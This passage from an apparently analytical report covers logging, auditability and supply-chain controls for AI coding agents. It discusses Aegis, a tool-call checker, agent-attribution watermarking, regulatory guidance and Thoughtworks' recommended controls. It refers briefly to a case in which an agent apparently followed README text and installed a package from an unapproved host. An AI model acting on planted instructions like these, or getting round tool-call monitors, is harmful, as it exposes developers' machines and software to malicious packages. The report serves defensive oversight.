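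The added computing time doesn't seem to be a serious obstacle. Nian and colleagues report tests of Aegis, a program that checks tool calls before they run and writes signed, chained records. It added a median of 8.3 milliseconds to each call, blocked all 48 attacks in a prepared set, and wrongly flagged 1.2% of 500 harmless calls. But Aegis records tool calls, so it would still need help from the operating system to show what pip did after a call started it.

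Nian and colleagues also cite a source-code scan of six open-source agent projects that produced 617 security findings, 269 of them rated critical. About 64% of the findings concerned tools that accept unchecked input from a model. Only 134 findings were in the highest confidence group, and several of the projects are research software, not products that companies widely use.

The scan is weak evidence about logging. Nian and colleagues acknowledge that the findings measure security, not auditability, but argue that insecure software is unlikely to produce trustworthy records. That is plausible if an attacker can change the log. But a program with an unsafe tool can still accurately record every command the tool receives.

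They reviewed 11 earlier systems and frameworks and found that none covered all five of their requirements. Protection against tampering and coverage of the whole task, including retries and approvals, were the most neglected. They chose the requirements and judged the other work themselves, so another group might have scored it differently.

The proposed Auditability Card is a short document in which a vendor would describe the evidence its agent system keeps and what happens when logs are missing. A buyer could use it to compare products before signing a contract. The card could give vendors a commercial reason to fill the gaps, but it wouldn't create a common format.

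Missing records are difficult to reconstruct later. Nian and colleagues describe a method that hides statistical signals in agents' text so that an auditor can identify which agent wrote each part. It identified the right agent for 82% to 87% of the text in its main tests, but for only about 21% to 24% after the researchers removed all the agents' identifiers. The method couldn't recover a download address that nobody had recorded, even if it identified every agent correctly.

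### Official guidance and legal duties

Government agencies and industry groups have only begun to address agents. Shan mentions three efforts. NIST, the US standards agency, has started an initiative on agent security and identity. OWASP lists supply-chain and provenance failures among the ten main risks for agent applications. The Five Eyes countries (the United States, the United Kingdom, Canada, Australia and New Zealand) have published joint advice on adopting agents carefully.

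Work on identity could eventually help registries recognise agents, and OWASP's list gives companies a shared vocabulary for risks. But going by Shan's summary, none of the three provides a common record of an install. The log formats submitted to the IETF come closer, but they are proposals that developers don't have to adopt.

Neither of the two relevant EU laws currently imposes a general duty on companies to log what their coding agents read and install. The first, the Cyber Resilience Act, applies to manufacturers of digital products and, according to Shan, requires a machine-readable software bill of materials. This list of components would usually omit an MCP server that a developer used only while writing the product.

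The Act's reporting duties began in September 2026. Help Net Security's *Week in review* (2026) summarises an interview with Aurimas Bakas, head of the compliance company Copla, who says manufacturers need a register of every product version in use and a clear definition of when they become aware of an exploited flaw. If an agent added a malicious package to a product, agent logs could help with both by showing which builds contained the package and when the first alert arrived.

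The EU AI Act's logging duties haven't started yet and may not cover coding agents. Existing rules for payment cards or government cloud services can still apply if an agent works on a system they cover. Other countries and industries may have further requirements, so a regulated company should check its own obligations.

### How far ordinary controls can go

A company that applies existing supply-chain controls properly may decide it doesn't need any of these new functions. Thoughtworks, a software consultancy, recommended six measures after the attack on the Claude Code extension in October 2026. It advised companies to ask for evidence before trusting a dependency, make development teams responsible for their tools, control updates, limit what a compromised tool can reach, rehearse their response and monitor developers' computers.

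There is a good argument that these measures would prevent much of the harm, though Thoughtworks doesn't claim they are sufficient. If a mirror supplies only approved packages, and computers can't reach other sources, an unapproved package is blocked whether an agent or a person requests it. A company can block the package this way without knowing who wrote the README or what the model learned in training.

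| Gap | What ordinary controls can do | What remains |
|---|---|---|
| Attribution | Apply the same limits to agents and people | Public registries still can't count agents' installs |
| Abandoned MCP servers | Allow one approved server for each service | Someone must notice when an approved server loses its maintainer |
| Unsigned instructions | Block unapproved packages and unknown hosts | Harmful edits that need neither, such as a change to the project's code |
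| No common record | Limit the damage and rebuild affected machines | Investigators may not find the text that led to the install |

The argument for a strict list of approved packages is strongest for build servers, which need a predictable set. Developers try new packages more often, so a strict list would slow them down unless someone approved requests quickly. A looser mirror that fetches any public package would have supplied both the Clerk malware and the abandoned MCP servers.

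The controls also depend on some of the missing links between records. Thoughtworks recommends comparing activity on a developer's computer with identity, repository and cloud logs, and a shared identifier would make that much easier. Most companies should still start with the ordinary controls, because those don't require waiting for registries or harness makers. In the tidewatch case, blocking `pkgs.example.net` would have protected the laptop, but without a record of what the agent had read, nobody would know to correct the README.
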